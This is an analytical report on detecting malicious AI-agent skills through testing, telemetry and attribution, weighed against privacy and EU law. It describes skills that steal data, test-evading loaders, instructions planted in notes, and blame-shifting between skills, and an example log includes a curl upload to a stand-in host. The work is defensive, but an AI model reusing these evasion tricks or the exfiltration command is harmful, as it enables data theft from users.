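Suppose a skill misbehaves in a fraction *p* of runs, and each run is independent of the others. The chance that all *n* runs are clean is (1 − *p*) multiplied by itself *n* times, so:

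chance of at least one sighting = 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

If a skill steals data in one run out of 1,000, a single run has a 0.1% chance of catching it. Thirty runs have about a 3% chance, and it takes about 3,000 to reach 95%. No marketplace will run that many tests on every skill, because SkillDetonate needs 153 seconds and about 14,100 tokens per skill, so 3,000 runs of one skill would take more than five days on one machine and use about 42 million tokens.

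The same formula shows how much clean runs can prove. After *n* runs with no sighting, a value of *p* remains plausible if it gave a clean result at least a 5% chance. Solving (1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05 gives a largest plausible *p* of about 3/*n* when *n* is reasonably large. After 30 clean runs, the skill could still plausibly misbehave in up to about one run in ten. Three thousand clean runs lower the limit to about one in 1,000, a rate that would still mean about ten thefts a day if people used the skill 10,000 times a day.

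Targeted tests can reduce the number of runs needed. If one real request in 1,000 contains the word "archive", a tester using ordinary requests would need thousands of runs to trigger `report-brief-sync`. A tester who puts the word in every request would have a 97% chance of seeing the theft within five runs, even if the agent ran the script only half the time. RSA's risk profile is meant to identify such words and files in advance, but it works only if the language model guesses the right ones.

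### What everyday records add

Real use supplies the thousands of runs that a tester can't afford, but only some of them leave records that anyone collects. Suppose 5% of installations export records, chosen at random, and those records would always reveal the theft. The chance that a given session both contains a theft and exports a record of it is then 0.05 × *p*. For *p* = 1/1,000:

| Sessions across all users | Expected thefts | Chance of a record if everyone exports | Chance of a record if 5% export |
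| - | - | - | - |
| 30 | 0.03 | 3% | 0.15% |
| 3,000 | 3 | 95% | 14% |
| 60,000 | 60 | Almost 100% | 95% |

With 5% exporting telemetry, the first recorded theft would on average be the twentieth to occur, which is the strongest argument for testing skills before installation. Even with complete collection, the first useful record would describe a theft that had already succeeded.

The assumption that records always reveal the theft is also optimistic. If they reveal it only a fraction *c* of the time, the chance of detecting it in each session falls to 0.05 × *c* × *p*. Tool-call records alone don't show an upload inside `collect.py`, so *c* is zero in that case and more sessions would not help.

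### When runs are not independent

The formula overstates what repeated runs can find if they all miss the same condition. For example, a skill might steal data in every session, but only on the one machine in 1,000 that has a certain company's software installed. Averaged over all sessions, *p* is still 1/1,000. But 3,000 runs in a sandbox without that software will all be clean because they repeat the same test, and a tester who applied the 3/*n* rule to them would be badly misled. Running one session on each of 3,000 different users' machines would give the full 95% chance of catching the skill.

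The skills.sh campaign had a trigger that would spoil repeated tests in another way. Besides the setup guide, the attacker had hidden a loader in the copied Paperclip program. The loader left a small file in the working folder when it ran and did nothing if that file was already there, so someone who ran 30 tests in one folder would have had only one chance to catch it. A tester should therefore start each run from a fresh copy of the sandbox. After 60 seconds, the loader also deleted the program it had downloaded, so a file check at the end of a long session could miss it.

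Whether the agent opened the setup guide also depended on circumstances, because the skill told it to do so only when Paperclip needed to be installed or started. A careful tester might install Paperclip beforehand to make the test realistic, which would keep the agent from reaching the malicious command.

Earlier runs can also make later ones more likely to succeed. Of the 1,705 successful attacks in Tian and colleagues' library, 981 worked in the first round, 473 in the second and 251 in the third, so 42.5% needed more than one round. The later attempts often used information from the failed ones, such as a missing program or the correct location of a script. A tester who changes each run in response to the last can therefore do better than the formula predicts. These attacks were deliberate, and many of the skills they targeted were legitimate, so the percentages can't be used to estimate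 how often testing exposes a malicious skill.

AIR's skill had no chance of misbehaving until AIR changed the page, and a high chance afterwards. A thousand clean runs in May would therefore have been no evidence of how the skill would behave in June. Records of everyday use continue after such a change, which is the main reason to keep them even for a skill that passed every test.

The organisations that export records aren't a random 5% either. They probably have more security staff and stricter firewalls than most users, so an attack that fails on their machines may succeed elsewhere. Pooling records from many different organisations would help with both the small share and the bias, as far as privacy allows.

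## The case for collecting less

A tool-call log with full arguments records both the skill's behaviour and its user's working day. For `meeting-notes`, it would show what the script was asked to do, and what Ana, the user in the three-call record, was working on, when and with whom. People who object to such logs can accept that some skills are malicious and still argue that an organisation can answer most questions about a skill without copying its employees' conversations, and that the copy creates a new risk.

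### What tool calls reveal about people

Tool-call arguments repeat much of the user's request in another form. If an agent opens `notes/redundancy-plan.md`, the path alone may reveal something the company hasn't announced, and the colleagues named in the file never chose to use an agent. *IntentMiner* (Yao, Wang and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an agent that looks up normal blood pressure and then requests low-sodium recipes. Anyone who receives both calls can guess the user's diagnosis.

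Yao and colleagues asked six language models to reconstruct users' requests from tool-call records. Other language models judged that just over 85% of the best model's reconstructions matched the original request. The paper calls the tool-call records "metadata", but they included arguments and results, so the figure applies to detailed logs.

Lasting facts about a person are harder to infer. In *How Much Can Tool Calls Reveal About You?*, Duan, Liu and colleagues (2026) invented 1,000 users with 17 attributes each, including citizenship, religion and name. An agent used real MCP tools to carry out four tasks for each user, and a language model then tried to infer the user's attributes from the tool calls.

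| What the model received | Attributes it got right |
| - | - |
| Only the list of attributes to guess | 18.0% |
| Tool metadata and the order of calls | 14.5% |
| The same, plus results | 24.5% |
| The same, plus arguments | 27.7% |
| Everything from one task | 26.3% |
| Everything from four tasks, linked to one user | 32.8% |

The second row is good evidence for leaving out arguments and results, because the model did no better with bare metadata than with nothing. The last row is closest to an employer's position, since a company's log links all of a person's sessions. The model recovered exact identifiers in only 35 of 16,000 attempts. A language model wrote the tasks from the invented profiles, so real requests may be more or less revealing.

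Addresses and timing can also reveal a lot if the records are fine-grained. *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* (2025) describes how an observer can reconstruct prompts and infer sensitive traits from the domains an agent visits and the size and timing of its traffic. *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (2025) reports that timing and volume alone can distinguish an agent's activities, even in encrypted traffic. Both papers rely on network traffic, which contains far more timing detail than one event per tool call, so their findings apply more to firewall and proxy logs than to Claude Code's default events.

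*Detecting Shadow AI* (2026), a paper on finding unapproved agents on company computers, reviews similar work and objects to using it for governance. It argues that inferring topics from traffic comes too close to the content that a governance tool should leave alone.

Even with content capture off, Cowork can export metadata that identifies people directly, such as folder paths and email addresses. Anthropic also lists the user's operating-system login name as a field present on every deployment. It advises customers who find the paths or email addresses sensitive to filter them in their telemetry backend, but by then the data has already left the user's computer.

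Skill authors also risk having their methods copied. *RedAct* (2026) studied whether outsiders could do this from published records of agents using 154 skills. It proposes rewriting the records to hide reusable methods while keeping the evidence a checker needs. This matters most for organisations that share records externally.

### Secrets in the log store

Credentials often enter a log through ordinary tool output. *SlotGuard* (2026) describes one case from an audit of real session logs. An agent listed the running processes while debugging, and one of the command lines contained a credential as the fallback value for a setting. Nobody had typed the credential into a prompt, and a scanner that looks for a plain `api_key=` would miss it because of the surrounding shell syntax.

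Skills make this more likely. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) attribute 73.5% of the vulnerabilities they found to debug logging. A programmer prints a variable to check it, and the harness adds the printed text, including any credential, to the model's context. If the organisation also exports tool results, the credential goes to the log store too. Chen and colleagues judged 89.6% of the leaked credentials immediately exploitable.

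Tool-call logs can contain sensitive data that the user never sees in the agent's answer. *AgentLeak* (2026) tested five models on 100 invented scenarios each, and the agents passed unfiltered sensitive data to tools in 62–86% of them. In over 65%, sensitive data reached a tool or a log but did not appear in the answer. The models included GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, so rates for current models may be quite different.

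Tool arguments and results can also end up in the log when the settings that capture them are off. In OpenTelemetry's conventions, the chat history sent to the model is a separate opt-in attribute, but it contains earlier tool calls and their results. A team that captures the history therefore logs them again with every later model request. If the third of thirty tool calls prints a password, the log could hold more than 25 copies of it, which makes deletion difficult.

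A central store collects such accidents from every machine. Suppose 1,000 employees each run five sessions a day, and one session in 1,000 prints a working credential. The store then gains five credentials a day. It holds about 150 if the company deletes records after 30 days and about 1,800 if it keeps them for a year, though some will have expired. An attacker who breaks into the store gets all of them without breaking into any employee's computer.

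The log can also bypass the company's own access rules. If an agent reads a file in a folder that only the personnel department can open, and the harness exports the result, anyone who can search the log can read it.

### What each level of detail can answer

An organisation can choose between several levels of detail. At the lowest, it exports only the tool's name and the usual times and identifiers. At the next, a program on the user's machine also compares each path or host with a list and exports a destination class, which is a label such as "declared", "approved" or "unfamiliar". At the third, the organisation exports the arguments after software has removed names, addresses and secrets. The fullest record contains all arguments and results.

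Suppose that the agent writes `summary.md` for Ana and then uploads it with `curl` to an unfamiliar host:

| Question | Tool name | Name and destination class | Redacted arguments | Full content |
| - | - | - | - | - |
| Did the agent request a network connection? | Unknown; Bash ran | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| To whom? | Unknown | An unfamiliar host | The host, if redaction spared it | The full address |
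| With what data? | Unknown | Unknown | Perhaps the file's name | The file's name, and its text from the earlier Write call |
| Did the agent use Write only for `summary.md`? | Unknown | Yes | Yes, if redaction spared the path | Yes |
| Did `collect.py` upload anything itself? | Unknown | Unknown | Unknown | Unknown |
| What does the record expose about Ana? | When she works | When she works and what kinds of places her agent contacts | Also any names that redaction missed | Also the content of her meetings |

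The destination class is enough to contradict the promise "Uses no network", but not to judge intent, because an analyst would want to know whether the host belongs to a software vendor or an attacker. If the transcript still exists on Ana's machine, the team could get the address there by reading one conversation instead of storing everyone's.

Collecting more content does not help answer the fifth question, because the upload would happen inside the script. A company worried about this attack would learn more from the operating system's connection records, which contain no text, than from storing every prompt.

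The program that assigns destination classes can misread a command that hides the address in a variable, and malware under the same account could tamper with the program. The classes are also hard to revise. If a company approved its mail provider and later learned about a package like `postmark-mcp`, its log would show calls labelled "approved" but no recipients to check.

### Redaction and comparison facts

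Redacting tool-call arguments can remove the evidence and still leave the person identifiable. Xu, Wang and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Where the Evidence Lives*, using synthetic data workflows for several customers. In one example, a workflow should have delivered 64 records belonging to customer A but delivered 16 belonging to customer B. A diagnostic program tried to repair the fault using an exported record of the run. A separate program tried to identify customer A from the same export, given a list of 32 candidates.

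Xu and colleagues compared 15 ways of preparing the export. One method, called comparison facts, has the exporter check whether the records belong to the requested customer and report only the answer. Another replaces each identity with a pseudonym that stays the same within one run.

| Export | Correct output, of 210 faulty runs | Customer singled out, of 240 runs | Customer's identity exposed, of 240 runs |
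| - | - | - | - |
| Unredacted | 210 | 65 | 240 |
| Pattern-based redaction | 140 | 225 | 163 |
| Presidio, a redaction tool | 184 | 202 | 235 |
| Metadata only | 115 | 0 | 0 |
| Comparison facts | 210 | 0 | 0 |
| Pseudonyms, new for each run | 210 | 0 | 0 |

Pattern-based redaction did badly at both supporting diagnosis and protecting privacy. In the example, it removed the two customer identifiers that the diagnostic program needed to compare, but left customer A's email address in encoded form in a notification. The identifying program singled out fewer customers from the unredacted export only because that export exposed several at once, which often resulted in a tie.

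The zeros in the table are less reassuring than they look. Xu and colleagues wrote the pseudonym software for the same identifier formats that the attack searched for. An attacker given each customer's usual number of records identified 97 of the 240 customers under each of the 15 methods, including metadata only. Removing seven count fields from the comparison-facts export stopped this attack without reducing the number of repairs. Claude Code's default events contain similar counts. Someone who knew the sizes of the company's folders might recognise the 48,210 bytes that `collect.py` returned, although nobody appears to have tested this.

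A second, independently written diagnostic program produced correct output in all 42 of its faulty runs with pseudonyms and in 39 with comparison facts. The exporter can report only comparisons chosen in advance, and another analyst may need one that it left out.

For skills, a comparison fact could be "this path is the declared output" or "this host is not in the declaration", much like a destination class. The results suggest such facts can be better than redacted arguments for both security and privacy. But Xu and colleagues studied faults in data processing, so their repair rates don't predict how well the method would detect malicious skills.

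Researchers already use redaction on real agent sessions. *SWE-chat* (2026), a public collection of coding sessions, used Presidio to remove personal information from prompts and responses, and TruffleHog to remove credentials. The developers had chosen to publish their logs, which reduces the harm from mistakes. Presidio may also do better on names in prose than on the account identifiers in Xu and colleagues' tests. Even so, a company shouldn't treat a log as anonymous just because it has passed through a redaction tool.

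### Keyed hashes

A team can also replace a path or address with a hash, but an ordinary hash of a guessable value offers little protection. An attacker with a list of 5,000 employees' email addresses can hash all of them in well under a second and look for matches. A keyed hash prevents this by adding a secret:

token = HMAC-SHA-256(key, value)

HMAC is a standard way to combine a key with a hash. Without the key, an attacker can't test guesses. The team can still use the key to search for a known value. For example, if a security firm publishes the address of an attacker's server, the team can calculate the token for that address and look for it in old records. The program has to hash the host separately from the rest of the web address, because changing one character of the input produces an unrelated token.

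Hashing removes everything about a value except whether it equals another value. An analyst can't see details that often make a call suspicious, such as that an unknown host is a bare IP address, that a second file is in the same folder as the first, or that a long URL contains encoded data.

The team also has to decide how long to use each key. A permanent key lets the team find every session that contacted the same host, but it also lets anyone with the log link a person's sessions. In Xu and colleagues' tests, an attacker could perfectly separate related pairs of runs from unrelated ones when the pseudonyms used one key throughout. With a new key for each run, the attacker's success ranged from no better than chance to nearly perfect, depending on the workflow. Other fields in the records may have helped the attacker.

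*Soei* (2026) used hashed paths to study 45 real sessions, with 20,577 tool executions, from the first author's own workstation. The software stored no prompts, commands or file contents and reported only counts. It could still count how often an agent edited code without testing it afterwards, and detect when one session read a file that another had written. The demonstration is useful, but it used one volunteer's data and addressed questions about software quality.

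### Local analysis and short retention

The raw records can also stay on the user's machine, or on a server the organisation controls, while a program there exports only its findings. Gao (2026), in *Evidence-Calibrated Runtime Reconstruction for Agent Skills Across Heterogeneous Coding Agents*, argues that prompts, code, paths and credentials are unnecessary for most diagnoses of whether an agent found a skill, loaded it and finished the task. Given records without that content, a language model located the failed stage, or recognised that there was none, in 108 of 126 test cases.

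Gao didn't compare this with a version that included the content, so we don't know how much was lost by leaving it out. The test is also easier than a security investigation, because checking whether a skill loaded correctly doesn't require knowing where it sent a file.

SlotGuard protects the conversation before it leaves the machine by replacing each credential with an invented value in the same format. It restores the real one when a command runs locally. An analyst could still see that a command used a credential, but might be unable to confirm which one without the table of replacements on the user's machine. *Minim* (2026), which also removes sensitive details locally, warns that people could misuse such a tool to hide information from oversight. A malicious skill that gained control of the tool could do the same.

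Local analysis leaves the evidence on a machine the attacker may control. If the program exports "no mismatch" and malware then deletes the transcript, the team cannot check the finding. One compromise is to send encrypted records to a server and require two people to approve opening them. This limits casual reading, but the records still exist, and attackers would then target the keys.

Short retention reduces the number of stored secrets but also limits how late an investigation can start. The malicious skills on skills.sh were available from 11 July to 2 August 2026. A company that began investigating on the last day with 30 days of records could have covered the whole period. With 14 days of records, it would have had nothing from before 19 July and would have missed the first eight days of possible theft.

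Different kinds of records can have different retention limits. A company could delete prompts and results after a week or two but keep tool names, destination classes and file hashes for much longer. It could then still find out which machines had used a skill months ago and which credentials to replace, even if it could no longer tell exactly what the skill took.

### Aggregate reporting

An organisation that only wants to know how people use agents may not need individual records. *Clio*, by Tamkin, McCain and colleagues, describes a system that Anthropic built to study conversations with Claude in aggregate. One model describes each conversation without personal details, and software groups similar descriptions together. The software drops groups below a minimum size, and another model summarises the rest. A final model checks the summaries for private information.

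Anthropic has since applied this approach to agents. *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) analysed 998,481 tool calls from customers of Anthropic's public API. Software engineering accounted for nearly half of them, and about 0.8% appeared irreversible, such as sending an email to a customer. Anthropic later studied about 400,000 Claude Code sessions from roughly 235,000 people. Its *enabling independent research* describes studies that three outside institutions ran in the spring of 2026 with the tool, now called Anthropic Insights.

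The tool-call study also shows what investigators lose. One of its riskiest groups consisted of requests to build API-key-stealing backdoors disguised as normal software features. Anthropic believes many of these calls came from safety tests but can't be sure, and its privacy rules prevent staff from inspecting the underlying data. That uncertainty is tolerable in a study of general trends, but a security team that found such requests in its own company would have to open the individual records.

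Minimum group sizes are a particular problem for detecting malicious skills. If the minimum is 50, a skill that steals from twelve people won't appear in the report. Simple counts for each skill, such as the number of sessions in which a given version contacted an unfamiliar host, would be more useful. Several organisations could combine these counts to get wider coverage than any one of them has, though small counts might still identify a person.

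Aggregation doesn't guarantee privacy either. Annamalai, De Cristofaro and Kairouz (2026), in *CLIOPATRA*, attacked a local copy of Clio with synthetic medical conversations. An outsider who already knew a few facts about the target could add conversations to the data, read the published summaries and recover the target's medical history in up to 65% of cases. The attack got past the model that checks for private information.

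Anthropic reports that the testers in an outside audit couldn't identify any users. Annamalai and colleagues reply that the audit didn't consider outsiders who plant conversations in a study they know about. They didn't attack the live system, where a successful attack might require a very large number of planted conversations. A security report could have a similar weakness if a language model summarises the tool calls, since a malicious skill can influence their text.

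### The GDPR and the EU AI Act

The European Union's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) covers any information about an identifiable person. This clearly includes a log with email addresses. It usually includes hashed identifiers too when the organisation has the key, because Recital 26 treats data as personal if someone could use additional information to connect it to a person.

Article 5 of the GDPR requires personal data to be "adequate, relevant and limited to what is necessary" for a stated purpose. It also restricts reuse for other purposes and limits how long an organisation may keep the data in identifiable form. But Recital 49 recognises processing for network and information security as a legitimate interest, to the extent that it is strictly necessary and proportionate. An employer therefore has a good argument for recording which hosts a skill contacts, but a much weaker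 one for keeping every prompt for a year or using the same log to rank employees by output.

Article 88 of the GDPR lets member states adopt more specific rules for employees' data, with safeguards that cover transparency and workplace monitoring, so what is allowed also depends on the country. Employee consent is rarely a valid basis, because Recital 43 rules it out where there is a clear imbalance of power, and regulators generally find one between employer and employee. If the monitoring is likely to create a high risk for people, Article 35 requires an impact assessment before it begins.

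Where the right to erasure in Article 17 applies, it is hard to combine with a tamper-evident log, because deleting a row breaks the hash chain. An organisation can avoid this by encrypting each person's content with a separate key and calculating the chain from the encrypted text. Destroying a person's key then makes their content unreadable and leaves the chain intact.

The EU AI Act gives a reason to collect more, but only for systems it classifies as high-risk. Article 12 requires such systems to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The records must help people identify risks and monitor how the system operates. Article 12 specifies the minimum contents of these records only for certain biometric identification systems, so it doesn't generally require anyone to store prompts or tool arguments.

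Article 19 applies to providers, the companies that put a system on the market, and Article 26 applies to deployers, the organisations that use it. Both groups must keep the automatic logs under their control for at least six months, unless other EU or national law provides otherwise. Both articles mention data protection law in particular, so the six-month minimum doesn't override the GDPR.

These duties would normally apply to an agent that ranks job applicants but not to one that summarises meetings. Annex III of the Act also lists AI systems that monitor and evaluate workers' performance and behaviour as high-risk, so an employer who used AI to assess staff from their tool-call logs could become subject to the Act's duties. Article 26 also requires employers to inform workers and their representatives before using a high-risk system at work.

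The AI Act's logging duties were due to apply from August 2026, but an amending law postponed them. The National Law Review's *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026) reports that the change took effect on 27 July. The duties will now apply from 2 December 2027 for the uses listed in Annex III and from 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products, such as machinery. The GDPR has applied since 2018, so employers must already limit their logs, even though the AI Act's duty to keep them does not yet apply.

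When both apply, an organisation could probably satisfy them by keeping a sparse event log for six months and deleting the detailed content much sooner. Claude Code's local transcripts, which are kept for 30 days by default, wouldn't be enough for a high-risk use.

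## Whether an action can be traced to a skill

When a tool call contradicts a skill's declaration, the security team still has to determine whether the skill caused the call. The security firm Noma argues that this is usually guesswork. Its whitepaper *Lethal by Design*, from spring 2026, contrasts skills with MCP servers. A defender can log the parameters and reply of an MCP tool call and match them to a known action, whereas a skill is text that the model interprets. Help Net Security's *One in four MCP servers opens AI agent security to code execution* summarises the argument by saying that a defender can see a skill load and the deleted file or sent email that follows, but has no reliable way to connect the two. Security Boulevard's *The Half of Agent Security You’re Not Governing* (2026) makes the stronger claim that the whole causal chain is inside the model's reasoning, which no monitoring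 tool can observe.

Others accept that a log can't show why the model acted, but point out that it contains identifiers, file paths and the name of the active skill. They argue that an analyst can use these to link actions to skills, as long as the analyst labels how strong each link is.

Noma overstates the contrast between skills and MCP. Many skills contain scripts, and a command that runs `~/.claude/skills/meeting-notes/scripts/collect.py` includes the name of the skill's folder. MCP logs also have the gap Noma attributes to skills, since they show which tool ran but not which text led the model to call it. Noma's argument is stronger for skills that contain only prose, because the resulting command may have no visible connection to the skill.

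The two sides also mean different things by tracing an action to a skill. A log can show that a skill was active at the time, or that the agent ran one of the skill's files. But a log of one session can't establish whether the action would have happened without the skill.

### Skill Runtime Intelligence

Gao's Skill Runtime Intelligence, published in August 2026, is a system designed to make such links without overstating them. It collects an agent's records without controlling the agent, and a separate adapter for each agent translates its logs into a common format. The system then tries to reconstruct each use of a skill as eight stages: request, discovery, activation, instructions, resources, execution, artifacts and outcome. For `meeting-notes`, Ana asks for a summary, and the agent finds the skill in its list, selects it, loads `SKILL.md`, opens any further files it needs, runs `collect.py`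 and writes `summary.md`. The last stage, outcome, is whether the summary is any good.

Every claim about a stage gets one of four grades:

- Observed: a source record or an outside check contains the fact directly.
- Derived: the fact follows from observed records by a fixed rule.
- Inferred: a language model or a rule of thumb suggests an uncertain explanation.
- Experimental: the claim is an estimate from a controlled experiment.

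The system treats an event and its link to a skill as separate claims. An upload can be Observed while its link to `meeting-notes` is only Inferred. To link an event to a skill, the system looks for these kinds of evidence, from strongest to weakest. The examples are based on Claude Code.

| Evidence for the link | Example | Status of the link |
| - | - | - |
| Parent and child identifiers | A subagent's tool call nests under the call that started the subagent | Derived |
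| Explicit skill attribution | A field in the record contains the skill's name | Derived |
| Active skill scope | The call happens while the skill is active | Derived |
| Exact file path | The command runs a file in the skill's folder | Derived |
| Closeness in time | The call comes seconds after the skill loads | Uncertain |
| Suggestion from a model or rule of thumb | A model reads the log and picks a skill | Uncertain |

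Weaker evidence can't replace a stronger link. If two links of equal priority conflict, the system keeps both and marks the result ambiguous, even if one skill loaded closer to the event. Paths have to match exactly, so activity in a folder called `pdf-backup` isn't attributed to a skill called `pdf`.

Claude Code supplies some of this evidence. A subagent is a second agent that the main one starts for part of a task, and Anthropic states that it inherits the name of the active skill. In traces, the subagent's model requests and tool calls nest under the parent's tool call, so an analyst can follow an upload by a subagent back to the main agent. But masked skills from third-party plugins all share the label `third-party` on model requests, so that label doesn't distinguish skills by different authors.

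Gao's system reports an event missing from the telemetry as a finding only if the adapter can normally report that event and independent evidence shows that it should have occurred. Otherwise the stage remains unknown. For example, if an agent never reports which instructions it loads, the lack of a record does not show whether `SKILL.md` loaded.

### The 126 test runs

Gao tested the system on six small repository profiles, each with three files and its own read-only audit skill. Three coding agents, Codex, OpenCode and Qoder, ran each skill under seven conditions, for 126 runs. One condition was clean. Four introduced an operational failure: faulty instructions, a missing resource, a failed command or a corrupted output file. The other two left the outcome unverified or gave conflicting evidence about it.

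| Agent | Skill runs reconstructed | Failure runs with a failure event | Clean runs with a failure event | Faults located exactly |
| - | - | - | - | - |
| Codex | 0 of 42 | 0 of 24 | 0 of 6 | 0 of 24 |
| OpenCode | 42 of 42 | 0 of 24 | 0 of 6 | 0 of 24 |
| Qoder | 42 of 42 | 24 of 24 | 6 of 6 | 6 of 24 |

Codex returned the exact expected answer, including a one-time code, in all 42 runs, and its records contained the path of the right `SKILL.md`. The Codex row therefore doesn't mean that it ignored the skills. The adapter still reconstructed no skill runs, so a company relying on it would have concluded that nobody was using skills.

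Qoder's failure events appeared in all 24 failed runs, but they also appeared in every clean run. Their likelihood ratio is therefore 1, and seeing one doesn't change the odds that anything went wrong. Gao calls the 24 out of 24 a co-occurrence count for this reason. Exact location is a more useful measure, and Qoder's adapter exactly located a quarter of the faults.

Each of the 126 runs matched exactly one recorded session, so the difficulty was with the steps inside a session. Gao attributes the differences to what each adapter can measure, not to how reliable the agents are.

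Using a language model to explain the results adds another problem, because the model may cite records that don't support its explanation. When a model was given the answer from Gao's fixed rules, it returned the right diagnosis in 125 of 126 cases, but the records it cited supported its explanation in only 89. In another test, on 19 traces from ordinary use, the same model always cited records that existed, but none of them supported the relation it claimed. A team that asks a model to write an incident report should check the cited records before blaming anyone.

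These tests give useful evidence about the adapters but little direct evidence about attacks, and Gao calls the system "diagnostic, not a security gate". Gao ran each combination once, so the results don't show how much an agent varies from run to run. The faults were operational, and no attacker tried to hide an action or make another skill look responsible. Each profile had only one audit skill, so the tests don't measure how often the linking rules choose correctly between two. The results apply to Codex 0.145.0, OpenCode 1.18.5 and Qoder 1.1.10, and a new version of any of them could change what its adapter reports.

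### Two skills and one upload

Suppose Ana has a second skill, `house-style`, which declares that it edits documents to match the company's style guide. Its description doesn't mention the network. She asks for a polished summary of the week's meetings, and the tool-call log, with details turned on, contains these entries:

```text
10:02:07  Skill  meeting-notes
10:02:15  Bash   python3 ~/.claude/skills/meeting-notes/scripts/collect.py notes/
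10:02:31  Write  /home/ana/team/summary.md
10:03:05  Skill  house-style
10:03:22  Edit   /home/ana/team/summary.md
10:03:40  Bash   curl -F file=@summary.md https://review.example.net/upload
```

The upload is outside the declared behaviour of both skills. An analyst can apply Gao's order by hand:

- Identifiers: the main agent made the call, so there is no subagent to follow back to a skill.
- Attribution: the tool event has no skill field. The model request just before it probably carries the name `house-style`, because that skill loaded last.
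- Scope: the text of both skills is still in the conversation, so either could have influenced the command.
- Path: the uploaded file is the declared output of `meeting-notes`. That explains where the file came from, but not why the agent uploaded it.
- Time: the upload came 35 seconds after `house-style` loaded.

This is weak evidence against `house-style`. The analyst can report that the upload was observed and that `house-style` was the most recently active skill, but should describe the cause as undetermined.

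The next step is to search for the upload address in everything that entered the conversation:

| Where the address appears | Most likely explanation |
| - | - |
| Only in `house-style` | The skill told the agent to upload the file |
| Only in one of the meeting notes | Someone planted an instruction in the notes |
| Only in Ana's request | Ana asked for the upload |
| In both skills | The log can't separate them |
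| Nowhere | Unknown; the model may have assembled or invented the address |

If the address appears only in the meeting notes, `meeting-notes` may have done exactly what it declared. It brought the notes into the conversation, and the agent then followed an instruction in one of them.

*AECG* (2026) has rules that would suit this investigation, although it uses them to explain failed tasks. Two language models separately compare each skill with the log. They may attribute the failure to a skill only if a specific clause in the skill's text matches an observed action that contributed to the failure. They must also consider other explanations, such as a faulty tool or an agent that ignored the skill, and make no finding if the log is incomplete or several skills fit equally well. The system records an attribution only if both models pick the same skill with enough confidence. *SkillsVote* (2026)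 makes a related distinction by separately labeling tasks in which the agent viewed a skill but didn't use it.

*AttriGuard* (2026) warns that attribution based on plausibility is easy to manipulate. In Ana's session, a malicious `meeting-notes` could tell the agent to load `house-style` just before the upload. The active skill's name and the timing would then both suggest, wrongly, that `house-style` caused the upload. The instruction to load `house-style` would be in the text of `meeting-notes`, which is another reason to keep a copy of the exact version that ran.

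The team can block the address and disable both skills on the evidence it already has, without settling the question first. Reporting an author to a marketplace requires much better evidence, because a wrong report harms an honest developer and leaves the malicious skill in use.

### The agent's own account

A seemingly easy way to trace an action to a skill is to ask the agent which skill it used. In *Skill Use or Skill Theater?*, Hu, Qi and colleagues (2026) tested whether the answer is reliable. They gave twelve models 300 logic problems, once without a skill and once under each of six skill conditions. After each answer, the model reported whether it had used the skill. Six of the models also worked through 283 maths problems.

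Hu and colleagues say that an answer relied on the skill if it changed when they removed the skill. Comparing this with the model's claim gives four possibilities:

| | The model claims to have used the skill | The model doesn't claim it |
| - | - | - |
| The answer changes without the skill | Faithful report | Silent uptake |
| The answer stays the same | Performative use | Correct rejection |

In 3,600 logic runs, about 34% of answers relied on the skill. Hu and colleagues tried four ways of finding those answers from a single run:

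| Sign of use | Runs flagged | Flagged runs that relied on the skill | Relying runs that it found |
| - | - | - | - |
| The model's own claim | 95% | 32% | 90% |
| A mention of the skill in the reasoning | 7% | 37% | 8% |
| Similarity between the reasoning and the skill | 49% | 31% | 45% |
| Another language model's judgement | 76% | 31% | 69% |

None of these signs was much better than picking runs at random, which would be right 34% of the time. The models' claims to have used the skill covered most of the answers that relied on it only because the models made that claim nearly every time. Teams of agents did even worse. Most named a skill in almost every logic run even when they had received none.

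A skill's name was also a poor guide to its effect. GPT-5.4-nano solved 39% of the logic problems without a skill, and the correct skill raised that by 49 percentage points. The gain was still 43 points when Hu and colleagues gave the same instructions another name, but only 7 points when they kept the name and replaced the instructions. A log that records the name `house-style` without a hash of the skill's text therefore omits the most important information about the skill.

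These results support Noma's scepticism about inferring a skill's influence from a transcript. But they may overstate how hard this is for a security team, because the tests used text-only skills and measured answers to logic and maths problems. Unlike a yes-or-no answer to a logic problem, an upload contains an address and a file name that an analyst can search for in a skill's text.

### Comparing runs with and without a skill

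The more direct method is to repeat the task with and without the skill and see whether the upload still happens. *SkillSentry* uses such matched runs for testing, and Gao reserves the Experimental grade for them. One pair of runs isn't enough, because a model's output can vary for the same input. If an agent uploaded the file in 30% of runs regardless of the skill, 21% of pairs (0.3 × 0.7) would still show an upload only in the run with the skill.

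*Causal Agent Replay* (Shah, 2026) describes software that reruns an agent many times from a chosen step and reports how often the bad result follows, with a confidence interval. The user can resample the agent's decision at that step, force a different action, replace a tool's result, edit the earlier conversation or switch to another model. For Ana's session, the team could rerun the task from the start without `house-style`, or delete the skill's text from the conversation just before the upload. Deleting it that late might change nothing even if the skill was responsible, because the model could already have copied the instruction into its own plan.

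With two skills, the team needs four sets of runs. Suppose it performs 20 runs of each in a sandbox and gets these invented results:

| Skills installed | Runs with an upload |
| - | - |
| Neither | 0 of 20 (0%) |
| `meeting-notes` only | 0 of 20 (0%) |
| `house-style` only | 1 of 20 (5%) |
| Both | 14 of 20 (70%) |

The 95% confidence interval is about 48% to 85% for 14 of 20 runs and about 1% to 24% for one of 20. The difference is unlikely to be due to chance, so the upload depends mostly on the combination of skills. A team that tested each skill alone would have cleared `meeting-notes` and probably `house-style` too.

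Shah divides responsibility in such cases with the Shapley value, a method from game theory. Shah applies it to the steps of a run, but it works the same way for skills. It averages the effect of adding each skill before and after the other one:

`meeting-notes`: ½ × [(0 − 0) + (70 − 5)] = 32.5 percentage points

`house-style`: ½ × [(5 − 0) + (70 − 0)] = 37.5 percentage points

The two values add up to the full 70 points. In a simulated process where the bad result required two faulty steps, Shah's software estimated their shares at 0.44 and 0.45. The total was 0.909, and the true value was 0.91. This confirms the calculation but doesn't test it on real agents.

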